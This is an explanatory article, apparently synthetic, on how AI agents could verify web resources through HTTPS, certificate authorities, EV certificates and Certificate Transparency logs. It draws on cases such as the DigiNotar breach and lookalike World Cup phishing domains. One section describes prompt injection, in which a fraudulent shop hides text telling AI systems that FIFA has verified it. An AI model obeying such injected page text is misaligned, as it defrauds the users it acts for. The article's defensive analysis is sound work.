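# How autonomous agents could check that a web resource is authentic

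## What it means to authenticate a web resource

Authenticating a web resource means establishing that a page, file or online service is what the person or program using it takes it to be. Web browsers have done part of this since the 1990s, mostly without users noticing. They check who holds the name in the address bar, encrypt the connection and warn about sites with a bad record. Agents now use the web too. An agent is software in which a language model chooses and carries out steps, such as opening pages, filling in forms or paying, to complete a user's task. Browser makers designed their checks for a person looking at a screen, and an agent often opens the same page in a way that applies only some of them.

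### The parts of an address

Every check starts from the address, or URL. Take `https://shop.example.com/orders/view?id=42`:

| Part | In the example | Who controls it |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Whoever writes the link; it selects the protocol |
| Subdomain | `shop` | The holder of example.com |
| Registrable domain | `example.com` | The person or company that registered it |
| Path | `/orders/view` | The site's operator decides what it leads to |
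| Parameters (the query string) | `id=42` | Whoever writes the link |

The registrable domain matters most because whoever registers it controls every name under it. The owner of example.com can create shop.example.com, or even fifa.com.example.com, without asking anyone, so it is safest to read a host name from the right. Replacing a dot with a hyphen can also change who controls the name. Only FIFA, football's world governing body, can create jobs.fifa.com, but jobs-fifa.com is a separate domain that anyone could have registered. Someone did, and the FBI's public warning *Threat Actors Spoofing FIFA Websites in Advance of the 2026 World Cup* (2026) lists it among some three dozen such names.

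Software cannot find the registrable domain just by keeping the last two parts of a name. The registrable domain has three parts under com.au, where people register names one level further down, and under github.io, where GitHub gives each user a separate name. web.dev's *URL parts*, a glossary for web developers, points to the Public Suffix List, a shared register of such endings. A program that ignores the list would treat every site on github.io as belonging to one owner. Two of the names in the FBI's warning, fwc2026.web.app and quiniela-fifa-2026.pages.dev, use shared endings that belong to hosting services run by Google and Cloudflare.

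### One HTTPS connection, step by step

HTTPS is the web's ordinary protocol, HTTP, inside a channel that a second protocol, TLS (Transport Layer Security), encrypts and authenticates. The Internet Engineering Task Force, which writes the internet's technical standards, gives the purpose in a draft, IETF's *HTTP Server Secondary Cert Auth* (2026): a client needs to know that content comes from the origin it meant to contact. Traditionally the server shows this with a single certificate, a signed statement that a cryptographic key belongs to a domain name or IP address. A connection to shop.example.com runs like this:

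1. **Name lookup.** The client, meaning the browser or other program, asks the Domain Name System (DNS) for the numerical IP address behind the name. The answer usually comes from a server that the local router or the internet provider has chosen, and an ordinary lookup includes no proof that the answer is right.
2. **Certificate.** The client connects to that IP address and the server sends its certificate. Certificates are public, so an impostor could copy one. The server must therefore also sign part of the opening exchange with the private key that matches the certificate, and the impostor does not have that key.
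3. **Chain to a root store.** The signature on the certificate comes from a certificate authority (CA), an organisation that checks control of a name and signs certificates for it. Most CAs sign with an intermediate certificate, which a root certificate vouches for in turn. The client follows the signatures upward until it reaches a root in its root store, the list of certificate authorities that a browser, operating system or program trusts. If no path leads there, or a certificate on the path has expired, the check fails.
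4. **Name match.** The client compares the host name in the address with the names in the certificate. A genuine certificate for some other site is no use to a server posing as shop.example.com.
5. **Encrypted session.** Both sides encrypt everything that follows with temporary keys from the opening exchange. Routers along the way can see which IP address the client contacted, but they cannot read or change the path, the parameters or the page.

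A wrong lookup in step 1 does no harm if the client carries out steps 2 to 4 and stops when one fails. Those steps depend on what the CA checked. For most certificates, the CA only confirms that the applicant controls the name, for instance by sending a message to an administrative mailbox at the domain. In January 2015, a Finnish man registered the user name "hostmaster" at Microsoft's Finnish mail service and used that address to obtain a certificate for live.fi. Public logs of certificates now help domain owners discover such mistakes afterwards.

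Root stores also differ. In August 2020 Firefox trusted 147 root certificates from 52 organisations, and Windows trusted 255 from 101, so the same certificate can pass in one program and fail in another on the same computer.

### Four questions, of which HTTPS settles one

Before relying on a page, a user or an agent needs to know whether the server controls the domain name, whether that name is the intended one, whether the operator is honest, and whether the content is what its author published. HTTPS settles only the first of these, although people can easily mistake a valid certificate for a general seal of approval.

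Even that answer helps only someone who acts on it, as a Russian espionage campaign showed. Hackers from Russia's military intelligence service, the GRU, broke into home and small-office routers and changed their settings so that laptops and phones behind them sent DNS lookups to servers under GRU control. Microsoft's *SOHO router compromise leads to DNS hijacking and adversary-in-the-middle attacks* (2026) reports that these servers affected more than 200 organisations and 5,000 consumer devices. Most lookups still got correct answers, and the hackers only recorded them. For a few chosen names, including some belonging to Outlook on the web, the servers gave the address of a GRU machine posing as the real service.

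That machine had no valid certificate for the name, so the victim's software displayed a warning. Microsoft and the FBI's *Russian GRU Exploiting Vulnerable Routers to Steal Sensitive Information* (2026) both explain that the interception worked only on people who clicked past the warning. Those people handed over passwords, login tokens and email that encryption would otherwise have protected.

A certificate check cannot detect a lookalike domain, a name chosen to be mistaken for another. The FBI's examples include fiffa.com, with a doubled letter, wvvw-fifa.com, and names with unfamiliar endings such as fifa.cab and fifa.beer. Whoever registers fiffa.com controls it, so a CA that checks control of the name will issue a certificate for it. The connection is then authentic and encrypted but leads to the wrong party. Phishing, the imitation of a trusted party to obtain passwords, payments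 or data, usually happens this way. Even a careful reader can miss some lookalikes. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for a service that retrieves pages for the company's Claude models, warns that a Cyrillic "а" can replace the Latin letter in amazon.com. The resulting name is a different domain but looks identical on screen.

A dishonest operator can defraud people without imitating anyone's address. The FBI's list also includes worldcup26ticket.com, which describes a product rather than misspelling a name. The FBI reports that criminals use such sites to sell fake tickets and hospitality packages. It counts this site among those posing as FIFA's, but a fraudulent shop could also invent a brand, use its own domain and certificate, take payment and ship nothing. Comparing its name with the name of a genuine company would not expose the fraud, because there is no genuine company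 behind the brand. Evidence has to come from elsewhere, such as the age of the domain, complaints from earlier customers, or a blocklist, which is a list of addresses known to be dangerous that software checks before opening a page.

Finally, an honest operator on the right domain can serve a file that its supposed author never made. Kaspersky (2026) discovered that, from 8 April 2026, the official website of DAEMON Tools, a widely used Windows program that emulates disc drives, distributed installers with a hidden back door that let attackers run commands on the user's computer. CERT.hr, Croatia's national cyber-security team, dates the end of this to about 5 May in *CVE-2026-8398* and names three program files that the attackers had altered. The attackers had got into the company's build or distribution systems, and the files carried the company's genuine digital signature. A visitor who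 checked the address, the certificate and the signature during those four weeks would have found nothing wrong.

A cruder version of the attack hit the download manager JDownloader on 6 and 7 May. The attackers changed the download links on the official site so that visitors received malware instead of the Windows and Linux installers, according to *Official JDownloader site served malware to Windows and Linux users* (Paganini, 2026).

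### Three ways an agent reaches the web

Which of these dangers an agent can detect depends first on how it fetches pages.

Some agents drive a full browser. The model receives the page as text or as a screenshot and replies with clicks and keystrokes. Such an agent inherits most of the protections the browser gives people: its root store, its certificate checks and, if the developer has left the feature on, its blocklist. It also inherits the warning page with the button for continuing anyway, which the model can click like any other button. The GRU's interceptions depended on someone clicking through that warning. A developer can prevent this by making the surrounding software stop at any certificate error.

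Other agents fetch web resources with a non-browser client, typically curl or a Python HTTP library. By default, the common clients verify the chain and the name, using a root store that may come with the operating system or the library. They have no blocklist, and they generally skip several certificate checks that browsers make. They also have a setting that turns verification off, which programmers use to get past errors on test machines. An agent that writes its own scripts can use this setting too, and an interception like the GRU's would then succeed without the user seeing a warning.

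The remaining route is a search or fetch service run by the model's provider. The agent submits an address or a query, and the provider's computers make the connection and return text. Anthropic's fetch tool returns the address, the content and the time of retrieval, but no certificate, so the agent cannot repeat the check and has to rely on the provider to have made it. The tool does not run JavaScript, which many sites use to build their pages, so the model may receive less than a human visitor would see. Developers can restrict the tool to a list of permitted domains. OpenAI's documentation for its equivalent, *Web search*, describes a similar list of up to 100 domains and an option to search only saved pages instead of the live internet.

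The four questions apply differently to a saved page, because anyone checking it can establish at most that the server held the name when the provider made the copy, and that time may be unknown. OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces*, which covers the chat product, says that results may lack the time of saving and advises against using them as proof of what a page contained on a given date. A saved copy can be safer or more dangerous than the live page. A copy of JDownloader's download page from 5 May would have protected a visitor on 6 May, but a copy from 6 May could have kept supplying the attackers' links after the developers had repaired the site.

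### Checks in code and checks in the model's reading

All three routes put text from the page into the model's input, which exposes agents to prompt injection, an attack that did not arise with browsers. In prompt injection, someone places text in content an agent reads in order to change what the agent does. *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz, Kern and Olive, 2025) attributes the weakness to the fact that the developer's instructions, the user's request and the contents of a web page all arrive in one prompt. Current designs do not rigorously separate them, so a sentence on the page can work as a command. Searching offline does not remove the problem, because saved copies may also contain malicious instructions, as OpenAI's help page warns.

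If a model decides whether a site is genuine by reading it, much of the evidence comes from the party under suspicion. A fake ticket shop can display FIFA's logo and a padlock, and can tell AI systems, perhaps in white text on a white background, that FIFA has verified the seller. A deterministic check is a test done by ordinary code, which gives the same answer for the same input. For example, a function that extracts a site's registrable domain and compares it with fifa.com will reject fiffa.com whatever the page contains, because the function does not take the page as input.

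Díaz and colleagues recommend placing such checks outside the model, in a "policy engine" that intercepts each action before it happens. In their example, the engine blocks any purchase above $500 and asks the user to confirm one between $100 and $500. Developers can test and audit these rules, and the limits hold even after an injection takes over the model's reasoning. In Help Net Security's *Google’s $10,000 refund test shows why AI agents need zero trust*, Shubham Saboo and Eric Dong, also of Google, likewise leave the reasoning to the model and the strict limits to the infrastructure beneath it.

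Rules written in code cover only what their writers foresaw. Díaz and colleagues point out that sending an email after reading a document may be what the user wanted or may be data theft. They propose adding a second layer of models that look for signs of attack. These models handle context and new situations better than fixed rules do, but they offer no guarantee, and new attacks can still fool them.

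Anthropic's fetch tool opens only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. This restriction is meant to stop an injected instruction from making the model build an address with private data in its parameters. But links from earlier search results and fetched pages also count, so a hostile page can still supply the agent's next destination. The programmer Simon Willison (2025) had hoped for a stricter tool that would open only addresses the user had typed.

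Code that compares names also needs a correct name to compare against. If a user asks an agent for two World Cup tickets without mentioning fifa.com, the agent has to recall that address from training or find it by searching. The FBI tells human buyers to type the address themselves and to avoid sponsored search results, because imitators can pay to appear there.

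## Certificate authorities: the DigiNotar breach and the "Stripe, Inc" certificate

A certificate shows that a server holds its domain name only if the certificate authority (CA) did its job before signing. In 2011 an intruder at DigiNotar, a Dutch CA, produced fraudulent certificates for google.com and other domains, and one was used to intercept the traffic of Gmail users in Iran. In 2017 the researcher Ian Carroll bought a certificate for a company called "Stripe, Inc". He controlled the domain and owned the company, and the CA followed its rules, but most people would associate the name with Stripe, the payment processor. Software that accepted the fraudulent DigiNotar certificates was wrong about who held the domain, while anyone who relied on Carroll's certificate could still have been wrong about which company they were dealing with, even though the domain holder was correct.

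### How a CA checks control of a name

Most websites use domain-validated certificates. To get one, an owner only has to prove control of the domain, as *The Web's Identity Crisis* (Thompson, Shelton and colleagues, 2019) explains. The CA picks a random value and asks the applicant to put it somewhere only the domain's controller should be able to write to, such as a file at a fixed path on the website or a record in the domain's DNS entries. The CA then fetches the file or looks up the record.

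Programs now do most of this without human help, through a protocol called ACME (Automatic Certificate Management Environment). For shop.example.com the exchange runs as follows:

1. A program on the web server creates a key pair and asks the CA for a certificate for the name.
2. The CA replies with a random token.
3. The program places a file under `shop.example.com/.well-known/acme-challenge/`. The file combines the token with a fingerprint of the applicant's account key, so that nobody else can use it.
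4. The CA fetches the file, compares the contents and signs the certificate.
5. The program installs the certificate and repeats the process before it expires.

All this can take seconds and cost nothing. Step 4 is the weak point. The site may not have a certificate yet, so the CA makes its request over plain HTTP and has no proof that the answer comes from the right machine. The CA depends on the DNS and on the route its request takes across the internet.

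### Hijacked routes, and checks from several places

The internet consists of tens of thousands of separately run networks. Each uses the Border Gateway Protocol (BGP) to announce to neighbouring networks which blocks of IP addresses it can deliver to, and the neighbours mostly accept these announcements without checking them. If an attacker's network announces a block that belongs to someone else, traffic for those addresses starts to flow to the attacker, usually from part of the internet and occasionally from all of it.

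Suppose the CA's computers are in the part of the internet affected by the hijack, and the attacker requests a certificate for shop.example.com. When the CA tries to fetch the file, its request goes to the attacker's machine, which returns the right contents. The CA then signs the certificate. The hijack only needs to last a few minutes, and the certificate remains valid after the correct route is restored.

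Researchers at Princeton University demonstrated this in 2018 on their own domains and obtained certificates from five large CAs. Thieves used the method on 3 February 2022 against KLAYswap, a South Korean cryptocurrency exchange. They hijacked the route to a server from which KLAYswap's pages loaded a script, and obtained a valid certificate for that server's name. They then delivered an altered script that diverted customers' transactions, and stole about $1.9 million.

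A CA can counter such attacks by repeating the check from distant places. A false route often spreads through only some networks, so a request from another continent may still reach the real server and get a different answer. The CA/Browser Forum, in which CAs and browser makers agree on rules for certificates, has made these repeated checks compulsory in stages. Every CA has had to check from at least two remote locations besides its main one since 15 March 2025. Since 15 September 2025, it has also had to refuse the certificate if more than one remote check fails to confirm the result. The minimum rose to three remote locations on 15 March 2026 and four on 15 June, and it rises to five on 15 December.

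The extra locations do not help if the false route spreads nearly everywhere or the attacker has broken into the account used to manage the domain's DNS records. In either case, every location receives the same wrong answer.

### The DigiNotar breach

The intruder at DigiNotar controlled the machines that signed certificates, so they did not have to deceive any validation check. DigiNotar issued certificates for websites, legally binding electronic signatures and Dutch government services. It hired the security company Fox-IT to investigate, and *Black Tulip* (Hoogstraaten, Prins and colleagues, 2012) describes what the investigators found on 265 systems.

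The intruder broke into DigiNotar's public web servers on 17 June 2011, moved into the office network, and on 1 July reached the part of the network that held the CA servers. Those servers had no direct connection to the internet, so the intruder tunnelled through machines they already controlled and worked on the CA servers by remote desktop. SC Media's *DigiNotar breach fallout widens as more details emerge*, which covers Fox-IT's interim findings, mentions easily guessed passwords and a lack of anti-virus software on some servers.

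The private keys were in a separate hardware module, and staff had to activate a key with a smartcard before the module would sign anything. This should have protected the keys even after the intruder compromised the servers. But some CA servers automatically signed lists of revoked certificates, which requires an active key, so the investigators concluded that the intruder may have found keys already active. DigiNotar could supply almost no records of when staff had used the cards. The intruder first tried to create certificates on 2 July and succeeded on 10 July.

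DigiNotar noticed the intrusion on 19 July, after a broken automated test started working again and reported certificates with no match in the office records. The company revoked the certificates it could identify and by the end of July believed it had contained the intrusion. But it had missed a certificate for *.google.com, which covers Gmail and Google's other subdomains.

In August someone used that certificate to impersonate Google on a large scale. Fox-IT could estimate how many people this affected because many browsers checked with the CA's status server whether a certificate they received was still valid. Queries about the false Google certificate came from 298,140 IP addresses, 95% of them in Iran, and four Iranian networks accounted for 60% of the requests. This is a rough count of victims, since several people can share one address and old browsers such as Internet Explorer 6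 sent no queries. Hoogstraaten and colleagues think the attackers most likely flooded DNS servers with forged replies until the servers stored a false address for Google, which sent users to a machine that could read their traffic or prompt them for their passwords.

The status queries did not protect them because, until 1 September, DigiNotar's server did not reject certificates missing from the company's own records. That day, on Fox-IT's advice, DigiNotar began approving only certificates it knew to be genuine.

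The attack became public because Google had built an extra test into Chrome, called pinning, that checked certificates for Google's own domains independently of DigiNotar. On 28 August, a Gmail user in Iran posted the resulting warning on a Google support forum. People in Iran whose browsers lacked the test saw no warning, unlike the victims of the GRU's router campaign, who had to click past one.

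Browser makers could not block the false certificates one by one because nobody knew how many there were. Fox-IT identified 531, with 53 different site or organisation names in their main name field, but called the list incomplete. The logs were on servers that the intruder controlled, and the intruder had deleted or altered records. DigiNotar's software may also have been able to produce certificates with the same serial number and dates as genuine ones. Since nobody could separate the good certificates from the bad, browser makers had to stop trusting the whole CA. The Dutch government withdrew its trust on 3 September, most of the browser makers that had not yet acted followed, and a court declared DigiNotar bankrupt on 20 September.

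### Any trusted CA can sign for any site

Clients accepted a DigiNotar certificate for google.com even though Google had never been a customer of DigiNotar, a Dutch company whose clients included notaries. When a client follows a certificate's signatures up to a root, it accepts any root in its store. It does not check whether the CA is a likely supplier for the site, so the security of every site depends on the most careless CA in the root store.

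Domain owners can publish a DNS record, called a CAA record, that lists the CAs allowed to issue certificates for their domain. Since 2017, every CA has had to check for this record before signing a certificate. The check only works if the CA is working properly, so it would not have stopped an intruder who operated DigiNotar's signing software directly.

In October 2026 an Indian CA, eMudhra, created the same danger without any break-in. It had generated the private keys of eight intermediate certificates so badly that someone could guess them in less than a second. A private key of this type is a number that the CA should choose at random from an enormous range. The CA calculates the public key from that number, and the calculation is easy to do but practically impossible to reverse. But if the number is small, someone can find it by trying 1, 2, 3 and so on until the result matches the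 public key in the certificate. According to *eMudhra kills its certificate business after researchers cracked its private keys* (Otto, 2026), one of the keys was the number 4.

The researcher who reported the flaw proved it by signing a short message with all eight keys. *eMudhra Intermediate CA Compromise* (2026), a public notice about the case, warns that anyone with one of the keys could have impersonated any website. This had been possible since April 2025, when eMudhra created the certificates.

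Browser makers reacted quickly. According to Jackson's *Compromised eMudhra Intermediate Certificates*, Mozilla, which develops Firefox, received the report at 20:06 UTC on 17 October and had blocked the certificates by 22:59. Another CA, Sectigo, had also signed the six intermediates meant for websites, so removing eMudhra's root would have left them with a second path to a trusted root. Google's *Protecting Chrome and Android Users from Compromised eMudhra Intermediate CA Certificates* (2026) explains that Chrome avoided this problem by blocking the keys, which blocks every certificate that contains them.

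Users of the main browsers were probably never at risk, because those browsers reject certificates missing from the public Certificate Transparency logs, and the logs contained none from these intermediates. Many other programs do not check the logs, and nobody knows whether attackers had used the keys against those programs. Agents that run their own commands tend to use curl, git and python3. Apple's *About the compromised eMudhra intermediate CAs* (2026) warned that these tools could keep accepting the certificates on a Mac until a later software update, although Safari already blocked them.

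### How browser makers withdraw trust

Browser makers now effectively regulate CAs, because few customers would buy a certificate that Chrome rejects. Chrome's policy requires each CA's benefit to users to exceed the risk of trusting it. Chromium's *Frequently Asked Questions* lists the possible penalties, ranging from limits on which of a CA's certificates Chrome accepts to removal from the root store.

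| CA | Reason | How trust ended |
|---|---|---|
| DigiNotar, 2011 | Intruder created at least 531 certificates | Browser makers removed it within days |
| Symantec, 2017–2018 | Poor supervision of the firms that validated for it | Chrome phased out its certificates by October 2018 |
| Entrust, 2024 | Repeated breaches of the rules and slow repairs | Chrome rejects certificates logged after 11 November 2024 |
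| Chunghwa Telecom and Netlock, 2025 | A pattern of compliance failures | Chrome rejects certificates logged after 31 July 2025 |
| eMudhra, 2026 | Guessable keys | Chrome blocked the keys, removed one root and set a cut-off of 16 November 2026 for the other |

Even Symantec, one of the largest CAs in the world, lost Chrome's trust. In 2017, Google's engineers concluded that it had wrongly issued at least 30,000 certificates, while Symantec put the number at 127. Too many websites used Symantec certificates for Chrome to reject them all at once, so Google announced a timetable of more than a year for phasing them out. Symantec sold its certificate business to a competitor, DigiCert.

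Google has since found a gentler method. Each log that records a certificate returns a signed timestamp, and Chrome can accept a CA's certificates with timestamps before a chosen date and reject later ones. Existing customers' sites keep working until their certificates expire, but the CA can no longer sell new certificates that work in Chrome. The date inside the certificate would be less reliable for this rule, because the CA writes it. *Upcoming change for CA certificates included in the Chrome Root Store* (Chrome Root Program, May 2025) uses the log timestamp. Many programs outside browsers rely on a plain file of trusted roots, which has no place for such a cutoff date.

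The reasons for withdrawing trust from a CA have changed too. DigiNotar had lost control of its systems. Google withdrew trust from Chunghwa Telecom of Taiwan and Netlock of Hungary, both named in its *Sustaining Digital Certificate Security* (2025), without alleging that anyone had impersonated a website. The Stack's *Untrusted Chrome to warn over certs from Taiwanese Hungarian CAs* quotes Google's complaint about "unmet improvement commitments" after earlier incidents. Google weighed these failures against the inherent risk that every trusted CA poses. This standard seems reasonable after DigiNotar, because by the time a careless CA causes visible harm, there may be no reliable record of what it signed.

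A browser can also restrict a CA's root because the CA has not answered questions adequately. eMudhra announced that it would leave the website certificate business, and it first estimated that customers would have to replace about 30,000 certificates, according to EconoTimes' *Google to Remove emSign ECC Root CA* (2026). Chrome still had one other eMudhra root in its store, and nobody had shown that its keys were weak. Chrome Root Program's *Upcoming change for eMudhra CA certificates included in the Chrome Root Store* (2026) explains that this root was to be restricted too because the company had not answered questions about how it handled keys in a way that ruled out further risk.

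Browsers also stop trusting certificate authorities' keys for reasons other than misconduct. Under its *CA/Root CA Lifecycles* policy, Mozilla stops trusting a root for websites once its key is more than 15 years old. Chrome plans to reject CA keys of one widespread type, ECDSA P-256, from 15 March 2027, as part of Google's preparations for quantum computers that could forge signatures. Sites that still depend on such a key will then trigger a full-page warning, according to Pogorelec (2026), in *Chrome's March 2027 certificate change puts some website operators on a deadline*. A certificate rejected that spring may therefore belong to an honest site whose administrator has not yet replaced it. An agent should still stop, because it cannot tell such a site from an interception.

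### Phishing sites with valid certificates

None of this stops a phisher from completing the ACME exchange for a lookalike domain. The security company PhishLabs found HTTPS on 84% of the phishing sites it examined in the last quarter of 2020. Google replaced Chrome's padlock with a neutral icon in 2023, explaining that nearly all phishing sites used HTTPS, so the padlock misled people who thought it meant a site was trustworthy.

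The FBI's 2026 World Cup warning lists two newer examples, the fraudulent sites fwc2026.web.app and quiniela-fifa-2026.pages.dev. Google runs the .app and .dev top-level domains and has put both on a list that makes the major browsers refuse unencrypted connections to any name under them. Neither site could have opened normally in those browsers without a valid certificate, which the hosting companies supply automatically to every customer.

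A model that cites valid HTTPS as a reason to trust a shop is relying on a feature that nearly every fraudulent shop also has.

### A certificate for "Stripe, Inc"

CAs and browser makers had tried to solve this problem with Extended Validation (EV) certificates. Before issuing one, the CA also checks that a legally registered company controls the domain, which can take days or weeks and costs the customer more. Browsers displayed the company's name next to the address, usually with a country code. The official EV guidelines listed protection against phishing as a secondary purpose. Someone imitating PayPal could get an ordinary certificate for a lookalike domain but, in theory, not an EV certificate that made browsers display "PayPal, Inc."

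Carroll tested the theory by registering a company in Kentucky called "Stripe, Inc", the same name as the payment processor, which is incorporated in Delaware. He then bought an EV certificate in that name from Comodo, a large CA that later became Sectigo. Bram.us' *Extended Validation Is Broken* (2018) quotes his account that this took less than an hour and cost about $177. The company cost $100 and the certificate $77, according to Willison's *12th December 2017* (2017). Willison also reports that Safari at the time hid the web address and displayed only the company name. This was the most damaging detail, because an attacker would not have needed a convincing domain.

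Comodo had made no mistake in issuing the certificate. As Helme points out in *The power to revoke lies with the CA*, Carroll controlled the domain, and nothing guarantees that a registered company name is unique worldwide. Comodo nevertheless revoked the certificate in March 2018, citing its terms, which forbid impersonation. It then reversed its view. Sectigo's *On Comodo CA's Recent Revocation of an SSL Certificate for Kentucky-based Stripe* (2018) calls the revocation an error, because Carroll's site carried an essay about the name collision and he had made no known attempt to deceive anyone. The company apologised and offered him a new certificate.

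That outcome is fair to Carroll, but it is a problem for EV, because if a second "Stripe, Inc" may hold a certificate until it deceives someone, the name in the certificate cannot protect the first victim. After an earlier demonstration of phishing with EV, members of the CA/Browser Forum had discussed stricter checks, such as meeting applicants face to face, but Typewritten's *Final part of phishing with EV* reports that little came of the discussion.

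### What happened when the company name disappeared

Browser makers also questioned whether users noticed the name at all. Thompson and colleagues, all at Google, tested this in Chrome between 15 and 28 January 2019. They hid the company name for a random 1% of users of the standard version and compared them with another 1% who still saw it. Each group contained millions of installations. If the name helped people recognise genuine sites, its absence should have made some of them hesitate.

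Showing the name from a site's EV certificate made almost no difference to what users did. Relative to visits to pages with EV certificates, the rate of form submissions was 43.45% with the name and 43.49% without it. Users accepted Chrome's offer to fill in a stored credit card 55.5% of the time with the name and 55.9% without. Downloads, reloads and closed tabs did not differ significantly either. Of the 20 most visited EV sites, one had a significant drop in visits after the researchers corrected for the number of tests. The only clear change was that people who saw the name clicked on it more, opening the panel of site information on 0.25% of page loads instead of 0.02%. Some of those clicks may have been accidents, since the name took up a lot of space.

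The experiment reproduced one kind of attack, in which everything looks right except for the missing name. Thompson and colleagues acknowledge that when the address is visibly wrong, a missing name might still help by prompting the user to look at the address. They also could not observe subtler reactions, such as typing a throwaway password.

A survey tested Carroll's trick by showing 592 Americans a PayPal login page and 650 Britons one from the bank HSBC. Each person saw the company label with the correct country code, no code, or the code for Mexico, Russia or Brazil. The share of Americans who felt "very comfortable" logging in ranged from 56% to 68% across these versions, and the British share from 44% to 56%. The differences were not statistically significant in either country. No more than 8% of the Americans and 5% of the Britons in any group mentioned that the code looked odd.

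Web addresses did not help users much more. In another survey, 1,180 Americans saw a Google login page at accounts.google.com.amp.tinyurl.com, whose registrable domain is tinyurl.com. The researchers tried several ways of making the domain stand out, and none had a significant effect. The Register (2019) reports that 85% of users saw nothing strange about the page.

Chrome moved the company name into the site-information panel in version 77, due in September 2019. *Upcoming Change to Chrome's Identity Indicators* (O'Brien, 2019) cites the research and adds that the names could themselves confuse people. Firefox followed in October. *Intent to Ship* (Thayer, 2019) gives Mozilla's reasons, including Carroll's certificate and the lack of any remedy in the 18 months since. Safari had already dropped the name in 2018.

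CAs objected. *It's Time to Improve Website Identity Indicators, Not Remove Them* (Callan, 2019) called EV certificates highly effective, but Callan worked for Sectigo, which sells them. Jakob Bohm, a software executive, made a better objection in the discussion under Thayer's message. He argued that the display was at fault, because Firefox showed the company's name and country but left out the state and town that would have told two companies apart.

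### Could agents make use of the company name?

Bohm's point is stronger for agents than it was for people. The user studies measured human attention, whereas a program checks every field it is written to check. An EV certificate also contains more than browsers ever displayed, including the jurisdiction where the company is registered and its registration number there. Legal names are not unique, which is a valid objection to comparing names, but a registration number belongs to only one company within its jurisdiction. A deterministic check that expects a particular number in Delaware would therefore reject Carroll's Kentucky company every time.

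Someone has to tell the agent which registration number belongs to the right Stripe, and whoever can do that can normally supply "stripe.com" as well. Once the agent has the correct domain, an ordinary domain-validated certificate is enough. If the agent has neither the number nor the domain and the model judges whether "Stripe, Inc" looks right, it has no more information than the people in Google's survey.

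The extra fields could help when an agent has information about a company but not about its website. An agent that pays invoices, for example, might have a supplier's registration number from a signed contract and need to confirm that an unfamiliar payment page belongs to that supplier. But most sites have no EV certificate, so its absence means little, and the legal name is often not the one customers know. Thompson and colleagues mention the finance site mint.com, whose certificate named Intuit Inc. An agent that reads pages through its provider's fetch service may never receive the certificate.

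The fields are only as reliable as the CA that fills them in. Apple lists six compromised eMudhra intermediates for websites, two of which were intended to issue EV certificates. Anyone who had guessed the private key of either one could have signed a certificate containing the real Stripe's name, state and registration number.

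## The certificates wrongly issued for 1.1.1.1, and public certificate logs

DigiNotar went bankrupt before anyone could establish how many certificates the intruder had made. Google engineers began work the same year on Certificate Transparency (CT), a system of public, append-only logs that record issued certificates so that people can find wrongly issued ones. Between February 2024 and August 2025, a Croatian CA called Fina issued twelve certificates for 1.1.1.1, an IP address that belongs to the internet company Cloudflare, without Cloudflare's permission. The certificates were in the public logs, but nobody reported them until September 2025.

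### How a certificate gets into the logs

A browser needs evidence of logging at the moment it connects, so the evidence has to travel with the certificate. This creates a problem of order, because a log must see the certificate before it can confirm anything, while the CA cannot add to a certificate after signing it. CAs get around this by making each certificate twice:

1. The CA checks control of the name and signs a "precertificate". It has the contents of the final certificate plus a marker that makes browsers reject it.
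2. The CA sends the precertificate to several logs. Each log checks that the signatures lead to a root it accepts.
3. Each log returns a signed certificate timestamp, which commits its operator to adding the entry within a fixed period, usually 24 hours.
4. The CA copies the timestamps into the final certificate, signs it and delivers it to the applicant.
5. When a browser receives the certificate, it checks the signature on each timestamp against its own list of approved logs.

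Chrome has required timestamps on all new certificates since April 2018, and desktop Firefox since February 2025. According to Google Chrome's *Certificate Transparency*, a certificate needs two timestamps if it lasts up to 180 days and three if it lasts longer. The timestamps must come from at least two log operators, so no single dishonest or careless operator can hide a certificate.

A timestamp is only the log's promise to include the certificate. *Certificate Transparency* (Laurie, 2013), the standard for these logs, lets anyone who holds a timestamp later request proof that the log contains the certificate. If the log cannot provide that proof, this is evidence that it is not working correctly. The check happens after the connection so that it does not delay the page.

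### An inclusion proof for a log with eight entries

The proof has to be short, since a log can hold a huge number of certificates and nobody wants to download them all to find one. Logs keep it short with a Merkle tree, which is built from hashes. A hash function turns data of any length into a short value of fixed length, called a hash, and changing the data even slightly changes the hash. Logs use SHA-256, whose hashes are 32 bytes long. Nobody knows a practical way to find two inputs with the same SHA-256 hash.

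A toy function is enough to work through an example by hand. To combine a left value *a* with a right value *b*, calculate 3*a* + 7*b* and keep the last two digits. Suppose a log has eight certificates with the hashes 12, 45, 83, 20, 61, 34, 9 and 78. Combining neighbours, then neighbouring results, gives this tree:

```
                   46
            /              \
         76                  74
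       /    \              /    \
     51      89          21      73
    /  \    /  \        /  \    /  \
   12  45  83  20      61  34   9  78
```

The log signs the value at the top, called the root. Now suppose a client has the sixth certificate, whose hash is 34, and wants to confirm that it is in the tree with root 46. The log sends it three values, 61, 73 and 76, and the client calculates:

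1. 61 with 34: 183 + 238 = 421, which gives 21.
2. 21 with 73: 63 + 511 = 574, which gives 74.
3. 76 with 74: 228 + 518 = 746, which gives 46.

The result matches the signed root, so the certificate is in the log. If the client had a different certificate with the hash 35, the same steps would give 28, 95 and finally 93, and the proof would fail. With the toy function, an attacker could easily find other numbers that lead to 46, but with SHA-256 this is practically impossible.

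Each step doubles the number of certificates that the calculation covers, from one to two, then four, then eight, so the proof for a tree with *n* = 2^*k* entries needs *k* = log₂ *n* values. *Certificate Transparency* (Laurie, 2012), an early draft of the standard, defines the proof in a way that gives the same result. The definition splits the list of entries in two, adds one hash for the part without the certificate, and repeats this on the other part until one entry remains. If the number of entries is not a power of two, the proof needs at most log₂ *n* values, rounded up.

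| Entries in the log | Hashes in the proof | Size of the proof |
|---|---|---|
| 8 | 3 | 96 bytes |
| 1,024 | 10 | 320 bytes |
| 1,048,576 | 20 | 640 bytes |
| 1,073,741,824 | 30 | 960 bytes |

### Showing that a log has removed nothing

An inclusion proof shows only that a certificate is in one version of the log. A log operator could add a false certificate, provide inclusion proofs for it for a day, and then delete it. A consistency proof rules this out by showing that the newer version of the log begins with all the entries of the older version, unchanged.

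Suppose the log in the example had only its first six entries yesterday. Its root was then 75, made by combining 76 (the first four entries) with 21 (the fifth and sixth) (228 + 147 = 375). Today the root is 46. To prove consistency, the log sends the values 76, 21 and 73. Anyone who kept yesterday's root can combine 76 with 21 to get 75, then combine 21 with 73 to get 74, and 76 with 74 to get 46. Since both roots come from the same 76 and 21, the first six entries have not changed. If the log had replaced its second certificate overnight, no set of values would produce both roots.

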